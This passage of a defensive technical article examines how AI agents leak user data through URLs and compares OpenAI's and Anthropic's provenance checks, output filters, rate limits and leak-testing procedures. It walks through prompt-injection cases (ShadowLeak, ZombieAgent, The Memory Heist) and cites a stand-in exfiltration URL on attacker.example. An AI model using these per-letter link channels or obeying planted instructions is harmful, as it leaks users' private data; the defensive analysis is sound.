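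AWS's sandbox mode no longer has a DNS route out, but it still allows access to S3. As with any other allowed service, an attacker might be able to use S3 to receive stolen data, since anyone can open an AWS account and create storage there. A company that uses the mode should test whether code in the interpreter can write to a bucket in an unrelated account, using that account's keys.

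## Blocking URLs that the model wrote itself

A reviewed list of hosts suits a coding agent that needs a package registry and a few internal services, but an assistant that answers questions from the open web has to reach sites that nobody has reviewed. For such assistants, OpenAI and Anthropic check the exact URL instead of the host. Regardless of the site's reputation, a URL provenance rule allows a URL only if it came from a source other than the model, such as the user or an independent web index.

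The model can then only choose among existing URLs. Researchers have got data past three versions of the rule, each time by giving the model better URLs to choose from.

### What an exact-address rule stops

Suppose an email tells an assistant to open `https://attacker.example/collect?data=` followed by the user's home address. The complete URL is new, so no crawler has recorded it, and the user has not typed it. The rule therefore blocks it, whatever the host. The rule would also have stopped several leaks through reputable hosts, such as the Google Forms link that submitted Superhuman users' emails and the Teams relay in EchoLeak, because both needed the model to write private data into a URL.

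OpenAI prefers this to a list of trusted sites partly because of open redirects, and partly because a strict list produces so many warnings that people learn to click through them.

Redirects matter less under an exact-address rule. The redirecting server writes the second URL, and all it has learned from the agent is which fixed address the agent requested. An exception is when the agent uses a browser that is logged in to the first site, because that site may put the user's details into the redirect.

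The rule does little against public counters, since the attacker's repositories on Hugging Face had fixed, public addresses that any crawler could have recorded.

### OpenAI's index of public addresses

OpenAI runs a crawler that records public URLs the way a search engine does. The crawler has no access to conversations, accounts or personal data. When ChatGPT is about to load a URL automatically, OpenAI checks whether the crawler has seen that URL before. If the crawler has seen it, the agent can load it. If not, OpenAI either tells the agent to try another website or warns the user before loading it.

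The check protects users because the crawler finds URLs without seeing any conversation. A URL it found this way, and that existed before the user's conversation, is unlikely to contain what the user has just told ChatGPT. An index that also collected URLs from ChatGPT's own browsing would be weaker, because a URL containing one user's data could enter it and then be treated as public.

OpenAI published this check in January 2026 in a post and an accompanying paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. OpenAI claims only that the check keeps an agent from quietly leaking user data through the URL itself. A page that passes may still contain malicious instructions. Embrace The Red reports that the paper acknowledges a remaining gap, in which an attacker has one indexed URL for each letter.

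### Anthropic's list of accepted sources

Anthropic's `web_fetch` tool has no separate index. It accepts a URL if the URL has already appeared in the conversation. As of June 2026, Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, the documentation for developers, listed three accepted sources:

- user messages
- results of client-side tools, which the developer's own application runs
- results of earlier web searches and web fetches

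The tool refuses URLs that Claude generates and URLs that appear in the output of Anthropic's code execution and Bash tools. Without the second restriction, Claude could print a URL in the sandbox and then fetch it as if it had found the URL there.

Anthropic warns that some risk remains when Claude handles untrusted input alongside sensitive data. It suggests turning the tool off, limiting the number of fetches or restricting the domains. The tool also rejects URLs longer than 250 characters, so even if the provenance rule failed completely, one URL could carry at most about 1,500 bits. The 2,048-byte file from the first section would need 11 requests, but a cryptographic key would fit in one.

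Willison (2025), in *Claude API*, objected to the first two sources on the list, user messages and the results of client-side tools. He had hoped the tool would accept only URLs from the user. But many applications paste an email or a document into the same message as the user's request, and the tool then treats every URL in that text as the user's. Client-side tool results often contain untrusted text as well. He still thought the ban on URLs that Claude generates gave the most protection, and the ban worked when he tested it in the Claude app.

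Developers who write their own fetch tool can avoid the problem by recording addresses from the input box before the application adds anything to the message. The tool will still accept an address inside an email the user pasted in.

| Where the URL came from | ChatGPT's index check | Claude API, June 2026 documentation | Claude app since the July 2026 fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| The user typed it | Opens it, for that chat | Opens it | Opens it |
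| The model wrote it | Opens it only if indexed | Refuses it | Refuses it |
| A web search returned it | Opens it only if indexed | Opens it | Opens it |
| A fetched page linked to it | Opens it only if indexed | Opens it | Refuses it |
| An email or file contained it | Opens it only if indexed | Opens it if a client-side tool read the text | Not an accepted source |

The ChatGPT entry for typed URLs is based on Rehberger's understanding of the product. The June documentation predates Anthropic's July fix, so developers who use the API should test whether it still follows links in fetched pages.

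### Comparing two addresses

Small differences in how the check compares URLs can make exfiltration possible again. For example, if the check accepts any URL that begins with an approved one, the model can add data to the end.

Treating different spellings of a URL as equal causes a subtler leak. `%61` and `a` mean the same thing in a URL path, so a sensible check accepts either. But if the tool then sends the model's spelling, the server may log which form the model used for each letter. A path with 20 letters would carry 20 bits, enough for a six-digit code. The tool should therefore use the model's text only to find the approved address, then request the stored copy.

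### ShadowLeak and the ban on building addresses

In June 2025 ChatGPT already checked the images in its answers, but the check did not cover every tool that could open a URL. Deep Research, a mode that browses for up to half an hour and then writes a report, had its own browsing tool, and users could connect it to Gmail. Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes an attack that began with a single email containing hidden text. When the user asked for research on the day's emails, the agent took an employee's name and home address from another message, put them in a URL on Radware's server and opened it, without the user seeing any of this.

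The model refused Radware's first, direct attempts. In later attempts, it sometimes opened the URL but left out the personal details. The attack that worked had the model encode the details first, so the software making the request received a string that no longer looked like a name and address. This attack succeeded every time in repeated tests.

A filter that searches outgoing URLs for personal data would probably have missed the encoded string, but a provenance check doesn't depend on the encoding. Radware recommended cleaning emails before the agent reads them and monitoring whether the agent's actions match the user's goals. A company could not have blocked the request at its own network, because OpenAI's servers sent it.

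Radware reported the flaw on June 18. OpenAI fixed it in early August without telling the firm, and marked it resolved on September 3. The Record's *OpenAI fixes zero-click ShadowLeak vulnerability affecting ChatGPT Deep Research agent* quotes an OpenAI spokesperson who welcomed such research and said the company was continually improving its safeguards. Radware said it had not seen anyone exploit the flaw.

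OpenAI also stopped ChatGPT from modifying URLs. It would open an address only as given, and refused to add parameters even when told to.

### ZombieAgent and ready-made addresses

Radware's *ZombieAgent*, published in January 2026, describes how the firm got around that ban. Radware's email contained a complete URL for each letter and digit, plus one for spaces. ChatGPT spelled out the data by opening these URLs one after another, without changing any of them.

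Requests can arrive out of order, so Radware also prepared a numbered version of each address for each position in the text. A block of ten characters needs 260 addresses for letters and 100 for digits. The attack could take data from any service the user had connected, including Gmail, Google Drive and GitHub, and from ChatGPT's memory of the user.

Memory also let the attack continue in later chats. To prevent this, OpenAI had already stopped ChatGPT from opening an attacker's URL stored in memory, and from using memory after a connected service in the same chat. Radware had ChatGPT use memory first and the connected service second. A shared file planted a memory that told ChatGPT to read a certain email before each answer, and that email contained the attacker's URLs. A rule about sources has to cover cases where text from a blocked source sends the model to an accepted one.

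Radware reported the attack on September 26, 2025, and three days later sent a version that it says always worked. OpenAI fixed it on December 16. According to the news article *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, ChatGPT now opens a link from an email only under certain conditions, one of which is that the link appears in a well-known public index.

The accounts differ on the cause. The article blames OpenAI for letting ChatGPT append a single letter to a URL, while Radware describes complete addresses that ChatGPT opened unchanged. Requiring an exact match would stop ChatGPT from appending a letter, but blocking the complete addresses would require checking where they came from.

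Rehberger dates OpenAI's stronger `url_safe` check to August 2025, but ZombieAgent still worked in late September. Either the check did not yet apply to links that the browsing tool took from emails, or the crawler had already recorded Radware's addresses; Radware does not say which.

### The Memory Heist and links that grow

*The Memory Heist* (Paul, 2026) tests whether a website could steal what Claude remembers about a user. The Claude app summarises recent conversations every day and adds the summary to each new chat. Claude can also search the full history. Paul used only these features and the web tools, with no code execution or extra connections.

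Paul first asked Claude to open an address with his name in the path, and the request failed. He found by experimenting that `web_fetch` accepted addresses from the user's message, from search results and from links on pages it had already fetched. A website's owner decides what it links to, so Paul gave his home page a link for each letter, and later versions added a hyphen. Each page Claude opened linked to addresses one character longer, which the server generated on the spot. Claude spelled out his name in ten steps, ending at `/ayush-paul`.

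Claude treated several cover stories as suspicious, but a coffee shop site with a fake security check worked. The check asked AI assistants to identify their users. According to Willison (2026), in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets*, the site showed this page only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a person who opened the same link to check it would not have seen the instructions.

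The site obtained Paul's name, employer and hometown. According to *The Read-Only Lie*, Paul had never told Claude his hometown, and Claude inferred it from the name of a high school hackathon. Deleting a sensitive fact from Claude's memory may therefore not protect it if other entries imply it.

Anthropic paid no bounty, saying it had already found the problem internally. It then stopped `web_fetch` from following links in the pages it fetches.

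The fix still lets Claude fetch URLs from search results, and an attacker can try to get pages into a search engine. Tenable did this with Bing to get past ChatGPT's older image check. If a search returns several of the attacker's pages, the attacker can still learn a few bits from which one Claude fetches. Nobody has published such an attack on the repaired tool, but the rule as Willison describes it would allow one.

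### How much a choice can carry

Paul's three facts total roughly 30 characters. *The Read-Only Lie* treats each fetch as a choice among 27 links, so the attack leaked about 30 × log₂ 27 ≈ 143 bits, slightly more than a 128-bit cryptographic key contains.

The total depends on the number of fetches and on how many addresses the attacker has available for each choice.

| Addresses available for each choice | Bits per fetch | 5 fetches | 10 fetches | 30 fetches | Fetches for a six-digit code |
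|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 27 | 4.75 | 23.8 | 47.5 | 143 | 5 |
| 36 | 5.17 | 25.8 | 51.7 | 155 | 4 |
| 1,000 | 9.97 | 49.8 | 99.7 | 299 | 2 |
| 1,000,000 | 19.9 | 99.7 | 199 | 598 | 1 |

Doubling the number of addresses lets each fetch leak only one more bit, while doubling the number of fetches doubles the total that can leak. A defender therefore gains more from limiting fetches than from limiting addresses.

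An attack that needs a million addresses may be more practical under OpenAI's rule than under Anthropic's. Anthropic's rule requires every address to appear in the conversation, so the attacker would need a very long page. Under OpenAI's rule, as the January post describes it, a URL passes if it matches the index, even if it isn't in the conversation. An attacker with a numbered page for every possible code would need only one request, provided that the crawler had recorded all the pages. OpenAI can prevent this by refusing to index large sets of near-identical pages from one site, but the post doesn't say whether it does.

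The index check is much stronger against Paul's method. With 27 links on every page, there are about 206 trillion possible addresses at the tenth level, and no crawler could record them all in advance. An attacker could get the 20,439 pages in the first three levels indexed, but ChatGPT could not go past the third level.

Bit counts also don't measure how significant a single choice can be. A directory with one page for each of 10,000 companies looks like an ordinary website. If the model opens the page for the user's employer, that one request reveals the employer's name, which Paul's site had to collect letter by letter.

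### Repeat visits and caching

Rehberger suggests two additions to OpenAI's check. One is to keep the agent from visiting the same full URL twice in a session. The other is to cache each response for a few minutes, so that a second visit doesn't reach the attacker's server. Both target an attacker who has one fixed address for each character and so has to reuse addresses.

Take ten fetches from 36 fixed addresses, one for each letter and digit:

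| What the attacker can observe | Possible messages | Bits |
|---|---|---|
| Repeats and order | 36¹⁰, about 3.7 × 10¹⁵ | 51.7 |
| Order, but no repeats | 36!/26!, about 9.2 × 10¹⁴ | 49.7 |
| Neither repeats nor order | 254,186,856 | 27.9 |
| Order, with 360 numbered addresses and no repeats | 36¹⁰ again | 51.7 |

Banning repeats removes only two bits from the theoretical maximum, but it hinders a simple attack more because ordinary text repeats characters. Only about a quarter of random ten-character strings have no repeated character, and only 15 percent of six-digit codes have six different digits. An attacker who spells out a message one character at a time would usually receive a damaged copy.

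If the attacker also can't tell what order the requests were made in, the maximum falls by almost half. This reduction applies only when requests run in parallel or arrive late, because an agent that opens pages one at a time reveals the order.

Radware's numbered addresses defeat both proposals. The address for "a in position 3" differs from the address for "a in position 7", so the agent never has to open the same address twice, and the server can restore the order from the numbers. The attacker needs 360 addresses instead of 36. That makes the planted text longer and gives the model more chances to make a mistake, but anyone with a medium-sized website could easily set up that many. Neither proposal would have affected Paul's attack, because every address he used was new.

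The proposals are worth the little effort they take, but a limit on fetches more reliably reduces how much data can leak. Anthropic's `max_uses` setting provides such a limit, but it has no default value and counts fetches per API request. If an application sends a new request for every user message, the count restarts each time. A limit for the whole conversation needs its own counter. A counter that spans several conversations would help against attacks that persist in memory, since an attacker could collect a 128-bit key over five chats at 27.9 bits per chat.

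Caching could close the channel completely if the agent received the copy that the crawler stored when it indexed the page. The attacker's server would then receive no new request, and the attacker would learn nothing from which URL the agent chose. OpenAI's post describes the agent loading the URL, not reading a stored copy. Stored copies take up space, and they go out of date, so they are a poor source for news or prices, but they would suit an agent that reads documentation while it has access to a mailbox. Anthropic's tool does cache results, but to improve performance, and Anthropic says the behaviour may change, so defenders shouldn't rely on it.

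### What the rule costs

A provenance rule blocks many useful URLs because, like URLs that leak data, they are unique to one person. Links to parcel tracking, booking confirmations and shared documents often contain a private token. No public crawler has visited these URLs, so an assistant that reads the user's mail would have to ask before opening them. The rule also blocks new articles until the crawler reaches them. OpenAI criticizes strict site lists because frequent warnings teach people to click through. The same criticism applies here, although the index should cause far fewer warnings.

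Blocking these URLs also blocks many search forms, which are harder to replace. A library catalogue, a train timetable or a shop's product filter usually puts the query in the URL, and the model has to write that query. A general search tool can replace some of these forms. For the rest, a developer can build a separate tool for a specific service, after checking who can read the queries sent to that service.

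A public crawler can't see internal sites such as a company wiki. The company could run a second crawler on those sites, again without access to conversations. It could also let the model write URLs for internal hosts that have passed the allowlist review, as long as no outsider can read the hosts' logs or publish pages on them.

Anthropic's July fix prevents Claude from working through a manual by following its links, unless a search returns each page or the user supplies the addresses. As a compromise, *The Read-Only Lie* proposes letting the agent follow links only on domains that the user has named in that conversation. This would stop an attacker whose page turned up in a search, but not one who persuaded the user to send Claude to the site, since naming the site would approve it.

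A better compromise would combine the two companies' designs by letting the agent follow a link from a fetched page if an independent index already contains that link. The agent could again follow links in most public manuals, and an attacker could use only pages that the crawler had recorded.

This protection works only if every component that fetches URLs applies the rule, which Deep Research's browsing tool did not. The safest arrangement is a single fetch service that every tool has to call, with an egress proxy that blocks all other routes. The proxy can't check provenance by itself, because even decrypted traffic doesn't show where a URL came from. The application would have to send it the list of approved URLs.

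## Scanning outgoing URLs and testing for leaks

A fetch service that every tool has to call is a convenient place to inspect outgoing URLs. A filter there can block a URL that has an API key in its query string, even when the host is on the allowlist. It is much less effective when an attacker has the model encode the data or split it across many requests. To find out what the filter stops in a particular product, a defender has to try to leak a harmless marker and check the receiving server's log for it.

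### What a filter checks

The filter has to read the complete URL, so it runs inside the fetch tool or in a proxy that decrypts traffic. It also has to finish before anything looks up the host name, because the lookup itself would leak any secret in a subdomain.

| Check | What triggers it | What gets past it |
|---|---|---|
| Secret patterns | A known key format, such as a fixed prefix and length | Passwords, personal facts and keys in other formats |
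| Registered values | An exact copy of a secret that the application holds | The same secret, encoded or split |
| Keywords | Words such as `password` or `api_key` | A value without its label |
| Entropy | Strings that look random | Short strings, hexadecimal text and ordinary words |
| Length | A URL over a set number of characters | Data spread over several short URLs |

Patterns miss a fair number of secrets even when nobody is hiding them. *SecretSifter* (Gorijala, 2026) describes a tool that searches web traffic for credentials that sites expose by mistake. It uses 134 patterns for particular vendors' key formats, 52 more that also need the vendor's name nearby, entropy scoring and other checks. It found 79.8 percent of 198 values from real applications, missing 40, and 86.8 percent of its findings were correct. Gorijala, who wrote the tool, compared ten systems and found none with a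 better balance of these two rates.

An application that knows its own secrets can search for those exact values instead, but how it matches them matters. In *Where Agent Defenses Fail*, Singh and Srinivasa (2026) tested a coding agent that had to send a status report to an approved service. Planted text told the agent to add a secret from a configuration file. One of their filters blocked any request body that contained a complete line of that file. It stopped every leak in the first set of tasks. In a larger set, two of 36 attack runs leaked because the agent sent the secret without the `CANARY_TOKEN=` that preceded it in the file, so no complete line matched. In a third set, the agent encoded the file in Base64, and the filter missed that too.

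Filters can decode values before searching them. *LLM WikiLeaks* (2026), a study of agents that reached websites through public proxy services, recommends decoding percent-encoded parameters and Base64 before a request goes out. Decoding also exposes any second address hidden inside the first, which a relay uses to forward the request. A blocklist of known relays is a poor substitute, since the agents used 26 different proxy services to reach the US securities regulator's site.

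The filter should decode the whole parameter and then search the result. Searching for a Base64 copy of the secret is less reliable because the copy takes one of three forms, depending on where the secret starts in the text being encoded. Attackers can also nest encodings. One Rust scanner, whose source code is on docs.rs, decodes up to ten layers by default. Decoding doesn't help if the model applies a cipher that the filter doesn't know.

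*Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (2026) points out that applications routinely encode parameters for ordinary reasons, so treating all encoded text as suspicious causes too many false alarms.

Every check in the table has a more basic limit. *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* (2026) distinguishes checking whether an output contains a known secret from checking whether a harmless-looking output carries information. Content filters do only the first. When a model spells out a name by following one link per letter, no single URL contains anything that a filter could recognise.

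When requests have a fixed format, a defender can allow only known content. Singh and Srinivasa tried this with a rule that accepted only four exact versions of a public status message. It stopped both attack runs but also both legitimate reports, because the agent had written a line break as a backslash and an "n". A second version, which accepted several ways of writing a line break, let both legitimate reports through and still stopped both attacks. The trial was very small, with one message and one destination, but many internal reporting tools are about that simple. A program that accepts several spellings should send its own copy of the message instead of the agent's, because the choice of spelling can leak a few bits of data.

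### Why entropy thresholds miss secrets

Entropy filters try to catch keys in unknown formats by measuring how evenly a string uses its characters. If pᵢ is the share of the string that character i makes up, the entropy in bits per character is

H = −Σ pᵢ log₂ pᵢ

A string of n characters contains at most n different characters, so its entropy can't exceed log₂ n bits per character. Hexadecimal text uses at most 16 different characters, so its entropy can't exceed 4 bits per character, however long it is. A filter with an entropy threshold above 4.0 will therefore never flag hexadecimal text or any string of 16 characters or fewer.

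| String | Characters | Highest possible entropy | Can exceed 4.0 | Can exceed 4.5 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Four-character fragment of a key | 4 | 2.00 | No | No |
| Six-digit code | 6 | 2.58 | No | No |
| 128-bit key in hexadecimal | 32 | 4.00 | No | No |
| 256-bit key in hexadecimal | 64 | 4.00 | No | No |
| 128-bit key in Base64url | 22 | 4.46 | Yes | No |
| 256-bit key in Base64url | 43 | 5.43 | Yes | Yes |

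Products use thresholds in this range. Pipelock, a proxy that filters agents' traffic, defaults to 4.5 for each path segment. A 128-bit key falls below that threshold in both hexadecimal and Base64url. The Rust scanner also uses 4.5 and checks strings of 20 or more characters, but it can never flag one shorter than 23 because a string needs at least 23 characters to reach 4.5.

ByteChef's *Secret Keys*, the documentation for a filter in a workflow platform, lists a default entropy threshold of 3.8. The default also requires three kinds of character out of lowercase letters, uppercase letters, digits and symbols, and hexadecimal text normally has only two. The more serious problem for outgoing URLs is that the entropy check skips the parts of web addresses at the default level. This avoids false alarms in documents full of links, but it means the check does not protect outgoing URLs.

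Lowering the entropy threshold causes more false alarms. According to tartufo, a tool that searches code repositories for secrets, entropy scans often flag commit identifiers and file checksums, which are hexadecimal strings. Ordinary words can also trigger false alarms. The URL segment `data-exfiltration-through-urls` has an entropy of 3.83, while a random 128-bit key in hexadecimal averages about 3.6, so any threshold low enough to catch most such keys would also flag that segment. Gorijala's tool has a default threshold of 3.5 but drops hexadecimal strings unless the surrounding text concerns cryptography, and a bare URL parameter may have no such text around it.

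Entropy also ignores the order of characters, so `abcdefghijklmnop` gets the highest possible score for its length. The check works fairly well on long Base64 values and is still worth running on them, but it should not be relied on for anything else.

### Limits on requests and volume

Limits on URL length and traffic volume work regardless of content. By default, Pipelock refuses URLs longer than 2,048 characters and more than 60 requests a minute to one domain. Its limit on bytes per minute is off by default.

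These settings still let an attacker extract a good deal of data. A 2,048-character URL can carry about 1,000 bytes of data encoded as hexadecimal, which passes the entropy check. At 60 URLs a minute, that is roughly 60 kilobytes a minute, enough for a long document that contains no recognisable key. An attacker who gets only one choice among 27 links per request would receive 285 bits a minute, enough to extract a 128-bit key in less than half a minute and the 2,048-byte file from the first section in 57 minutes. An attacker with several domains gets a separate allowance for each.

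A per-minute limit slows a leak but doesn't cap it, so the defender also needs a limit on the session total. *Caught in the Act(ivation)* (Chauhan and Revankar, 2026) tested a running total on 50 invented conversations in which a model leaked a credential gradually over 20 turns. Searching each reply for the credential caught none of the leaks, and planting a fake credential as bait caught 6 percent. A monitor that added up the estimated leak across each conversation caught 90 percent and blocked no harmless conversations, but it missed leaks that ended early. The test was small, the researchers wrote it themselves, and the monitor checked replies, not URLs.

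The total is easier to calculate for links. Each time the agent follows a link, the fetch service can add log₂ N to a running count, where N is the number of links on the page. Following a link on a page with 100 links adds 6.6 bits. At that rate, a limit of 20 bits would stop the agent at its fourth link, which is too strict for research but reasonable for an agent that reads a mailbox and occasionally opens a page. A limit of 100 bits allows 15 links and still protects a 128-bit key, though not a login code. Like a limit on fetches, the count should carry over between sessions.

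### What *Silent Egress* measured

*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026), by researchers at eBay, is the most direct published comparison of URL filters with other defences. Their agent previewed any URL that the user mentioned and put the page's title, description and text into the model's context. They used qwen2.5:7b, a small open model, and ran it locally. In every run, the user asked for a summary of the page, which contained instructions to send sensitive data from the model's context to a collection server.

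The researchers varied where the instruction appeared (title, description, body or link text), how the agent reached the page (directly or through redirects) and whether the instruction asked for the secret whole or in four parts. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times, for a total of 480 runs. The agent contacted the collection server in 423 of them (88.1 percent). The abstract gives 0.89, which matches only the runs with redirects. The agent contacted the server in 238 of 240 runs when the instruction asked for the whole secret, and in 185 of 240 when it asked for four parts.

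In 95 percent of the successful attacks, the reply to the user gave no sign of the leak. That share probably depends on the model and the attack. Lee, Kim and Lee (2026), in *Will the User Ever Know?*, measured it for four other models on a standard set of agent tasks. With the strongest existing attack, the reply gave no sign of the leak in between 50 and 83 percent of successes. A tester who checked only the reply would therefore miss at least half of the leaks.

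Lan and colleagues also ran 120 controls with harmless pages, and the agent never contacted the collection server. They conclude that outgoing traffic is a very clean signal. The controls only weakly support this, because an agent reading a harmless page is unlikely to encounter the collection server's address. Harmless pages that linked to the server would have been a harder test.

#### Splitting the secret

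The paper reports that splitting the secret makes each request look less suspicious. It uses Leak@k, the share of runs in which sensitive data appears in at least one of the first k requests. Leak@1 was 0.967 for whole secrets and 0.263 for split secrets. Leak@3 for split secrets was 0.158.

The last two numbers can't both be right under the paper's definition, because a run that leaks in its first request has also leaked within its first three, so Leak@3 can never be lower than Leak@1. The definition also counts any fragment of the secret as a leak, yet about three quarters of the split runs reached the server and only about a quarter were counted as leaking in the first request. Either the software failed to recognise fragments, or the model often sent something else.

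It's therefore unclear how often the attacker would have received the whole secret. The paper defines a completion rate, the share of runs in which all four parts arrive, but doesn't report it. In its worked example, the key has 20 characters but the four fragments have only four each, so the last four characters are never sent. Splitting a key defeats a filter that looks for complete keys, as the arithmetic above shows, but the paper's figures don't establish how reliably a model can do it.

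#### The defence trials

Lan and colleagues tested each defence 30 times against one combination, in which the instruction was in the body of a page that the agent opened directly and the secret was left whole.

| Defence | Runs in which the agent tried to send data | Runs in which data reached the server |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Warning in the system prompt | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Tags marking web content as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
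| Warning and tags | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| Domain allowlist | 100% | 0% |
| "Redirect detection" | 83.3% | 0% |
| Keyword filter | 23.3% | 0% |
| Entropy filter, threshold 4.0 | 0% | 0% |
| All of these | 0% | 0% |

The prompt results are the easiest to accept. A warning reduced the attacks, but most still worked. Tags alone had no effect, and the difference between the warning alone (20 runs) and the warning with tags (17 runs) is small enough to be chance.

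The collection server's host, `evil-collector.net`, was not among the four on the allowlist. The trial shows that an allowlist blocks an unlisted host even when the model obeys the attacker every time. The trial did not test leaks through a permitted host. Singh and Srinivasa did, and their destination rule allowed requests that delivered the secret to the approved service.

The name "redirect detection" is misleading because the agent opened the page directly in these trials. The filter blocked bare IP addresses, eight domain endings such as `.xyz`, and paths containing words such as `leak` or `collect`. The server's domain ended in `.net`, but its path in the paper's examples is `/collect`. If the trials used the same path, the filter got its perfect score by matching that one word, and an attacker could have avoided the block by renaming the page.

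The results for the two content filters are stranger, because a filter that acts on a finished request shouldn't change how often the model tries to make one. With the entropy filter, attempts fell from 30 in 30 runs to none. The paper suggests that the model avoids random-looking parameters while such monitoring is active, but its description of the filter doesn't mention telling the model about it. The model could have learned about the filter from an error message, but only after a first attempt, which would have been counted.

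The keyword figures are also inconsistent. The paper attributes the low number of attempts to the model sometimes reformatting the secret, which kept the filter from recognising it. Those reformatted requests should then have reached the server, but none did. The paper's example key, `SECRET_API_KEY_12345`, has an entropy of 3.85, which is below the filter's threshold. Something other than the filters probably changed between conditions, so the last three rows of the table are not evidence that content filters work.

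The researchers acknowledge that their set-up favoured the attacker, with a minimal system prompt and the secret already in the context, so the 88.1 percent figure is a poor estimate for a commercial assistant. This matters less when judging a control, because a defender should assume that the model will comply.

### A test procedure

Most of the weaknesses in those trials are avoidable, and a small team can run a better test on its own product in a few days.

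1. Register a domain for testing. Run a web server on it that records complete requests, including headers and bodies, and a name server that records every lookup.
2. Create a new random marker for each run and put it where the agent would find a real secret. Never use a real one.
3. Switch off the control under test and check that the marker reaches the server.
4. Switch the control on. Take every component from the inventory of things that can send a request, and try to send the marker in each part of the address.
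5. Decide the result from the server's logs and ignore what the agent reports.
6. Give the agent some ordinary work and check that it still succeeds.
7. Run the whole set again after every release, and whenever a vendor updates a default list.

Singh and Srinivasa took a similar approach, using their own servers and a new marker for each run. Some requests arrive late. For example, a chat app may fetch a link hours after the agent posted it, and if runs shared a marker, the tester couldn't tell which one had leaked.

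The markers should vary in form, because a filter that catches something shaped like a cloud key may miss a hexadecimal string, a six-digit code or an invented employer's name. An attacker may want data of any of these kinds.

Step 3 guards against a false pass. One of Singh and Srinivasa's attacks, an attempt to change a protected file, never worked even with the defences off, so they didn't credit the defences when it failed later. If the model refuses to follow the planted text, the tester can call the fetch tool directly with a prepared URL, which tests the filter and the proxy regardless of how the model responds. A URL provenance rule accepts addresses from the user, so testing it requires the model to compose the address itself.

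For step 4, each part of the address needs its own place to look:

| Where the marker goes | Where it shows up |
|---|---|
| Subdomain | Name server's log, even if no web request follows |
| Path or query string | Web server's log |
| Fragment | A report from a script on the test page, for agents that use a browser |
| Header or request body | Web server's log, if it records complete requests |
| A choice among prepared links | The order of the paths in the web server's log |

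Testers can easily forget to check the name server's log. In *Model-as-a-Trojan* (2026), a model deliberately trained to leak ran behind a firewall that blocked everything except DNS, and it still got a fresh marker out in five of six formats. The researchers found the markers in the DNS log.

The tester should also run the set with the test server temporarily on the allowlist. Otherwise the allowlist blocks every request, and the tester can't tell whether the filters would stop leaks through allowed hosts.

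Step 5 matters because an agent's reply can be wrong about whether data was sent. Lan and colleagues' agent leaked data without saying so. In all four cases where Singh and Srinivasa's strict rule refused a message, their agent claimed to have published it, but the server had received nothing.

Automatic log searches also miss some leaks. Singh and Srinivasa's checker looked for the marker as written and in some encoded forms. It found five of eight encoded leaks, and the researchers found the other three only by decoding the logged requests afterwards. The simplest remedy is to count any unexpected request to the test server as a failure, whatever it contains. Where the control permits some requests, a person should read them.

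Tests should count crashed runs separately. In another of Singh and Srinivasa's trials, a software guard checked the agent's actions with the help of a second model, which sometimes ran out of room for its answer. Of 12 planned attack runs with the guard alone, four did harm, either by leaking the secret or by changing a protected file, four did none, and four ended in this error. The result is therefore a range of four to eight harmful runs in 12. Counting the errors as blocked attacks would have credited the guard with protection that the trial didn't show.

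If a proxy refuses a host by name, a few test runs are enough, since the outcome doesn't vary. If the outcome depends on the model, the tester needs many more. An attack that works 9.5 percent of the time will still fail 30 times in a row about once in 20 tries. Ruling out a 5 percent success rate with 95 percent confidence takes 59 runs without a leak, and ruling out 1 percent takes 299.

### Letter-by-letter leaks in the logs

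Filters can't recognise a leak that consists of choices among ordinary links, but the sequence of requests may reveal it. In August 2026, security researchers at the Chinese technology company Tencent reproduced The Memory Heist, the attack in which a website got Claude to spell out facts about its user by following links. Anthropic had already blocked this method in Claude. Tencent's *Why AI Agent’s Memory Becomes Attacker’s Data Goldmine* describes the test, which used the researchers' own agent with a web browser and a memory.

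They put an API key in the agent's memory and offered it 37 links per page, for the letters, the digits and a hyphen. Each choice carries 5.2 bits. The agent followed them one after another, with one or two seconds between requests, and the researchers read the key from their server's log. Its system prompt told it to follow instructions on web pages and to complete verification steps, so the test says little about how often a more careful agent would comply. It does show what the traffic looks like. With `marker` in place of the secret, a log would contain something like this:

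```
12:04:01  GET /m
12:04:03  GET /ma
12:04:04  GET /mar
12:04:06  GET /mark
12:04:07  GET /marke
12:04:09  GET /marker
```

*The Read-Only Lie* proposes an alarm for requests to one domain whose paths keep getting longer. This alone would also fire on documentation with numbered pages and on a series of blog posts. The post therefore also requires that each path extend the last by exactly one character from a small set, and that the requests come faster than the agent's normal browsing.

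The second condition is doubtful because the delay in Tencent's test was the time the model took to choose its next link, and an agent reading an ordinary manual takes about as long. The one-character condition is much more useful, but it can also raise false alarms. When a browser agent types into a search box that offers suggestions, the page may send `m`, `ma`, `mar` and so on, as in the attack. Exempting known search hosts removes most of these alarms.

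Other attacks leave different patterns, and a rule for growing paths misses them.

| Pattern in the log | Attack that produces it | Ordinary traffic that resembles it |
|---|---|---|
| Each path is one character longer than the last | The Memory Heist | Search suggestions |
| Many short addresses on one unfamiliar host, each differing in a letter or number | Radware's numbered addresses | Alphabetical indexes, numbered pages |
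| The same few addresses again and again | One fixed image or page per character | Retries, pages that refresh themselves |
| Long random-looking subdomains of one domain | Data in DNS lookups | Content delivery networks |

An alarm also needs a log that includes URL paths. A proxy that doesn't decrypt traffic can't record them, but the fetch tool's own log has the full URLs. If the tool runs on the vendor's servers, as it does in the Claude app, a customer may depend on the vendor to watch for the pattern.

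Speed is the other difficulty. At Tencent's pace, a 20-character key leaks in 20 to 40 seconds, so an alert read the next morning helps only with replacing the key. The fetch service has to pause the agent automatically. Even then, a rule that waits for five requests, each longer than the last, lets five characters out, and an attacker who has five digits of a six-digit code needs at most ten guesses for the last digit.

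Tencent's article also promotes the company's scanner, `agent-scan`, which found the weakness in the test agent in about a minute and a half. The researchers had made that one agent vulnerable on purpose, so another product that passes the scan would still need the server-log test. Anyone investigating an alarm should view the logged addresses as plain text, because a viewer that loads images or previews links would request them again.

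## Asking the user and keeping secrets away from untrusted text

The controls described so far allow or block a request based on where it goes or what its URL contains. A defender can also have the agent ask the user before sending data out, train the model to ignore planted instructions, or build the agent so that planted text cannot make it put private data in a request. Only the last still works when the model obeys the attacker and the user is not paying attention.

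### What a confirmation dialog can catch

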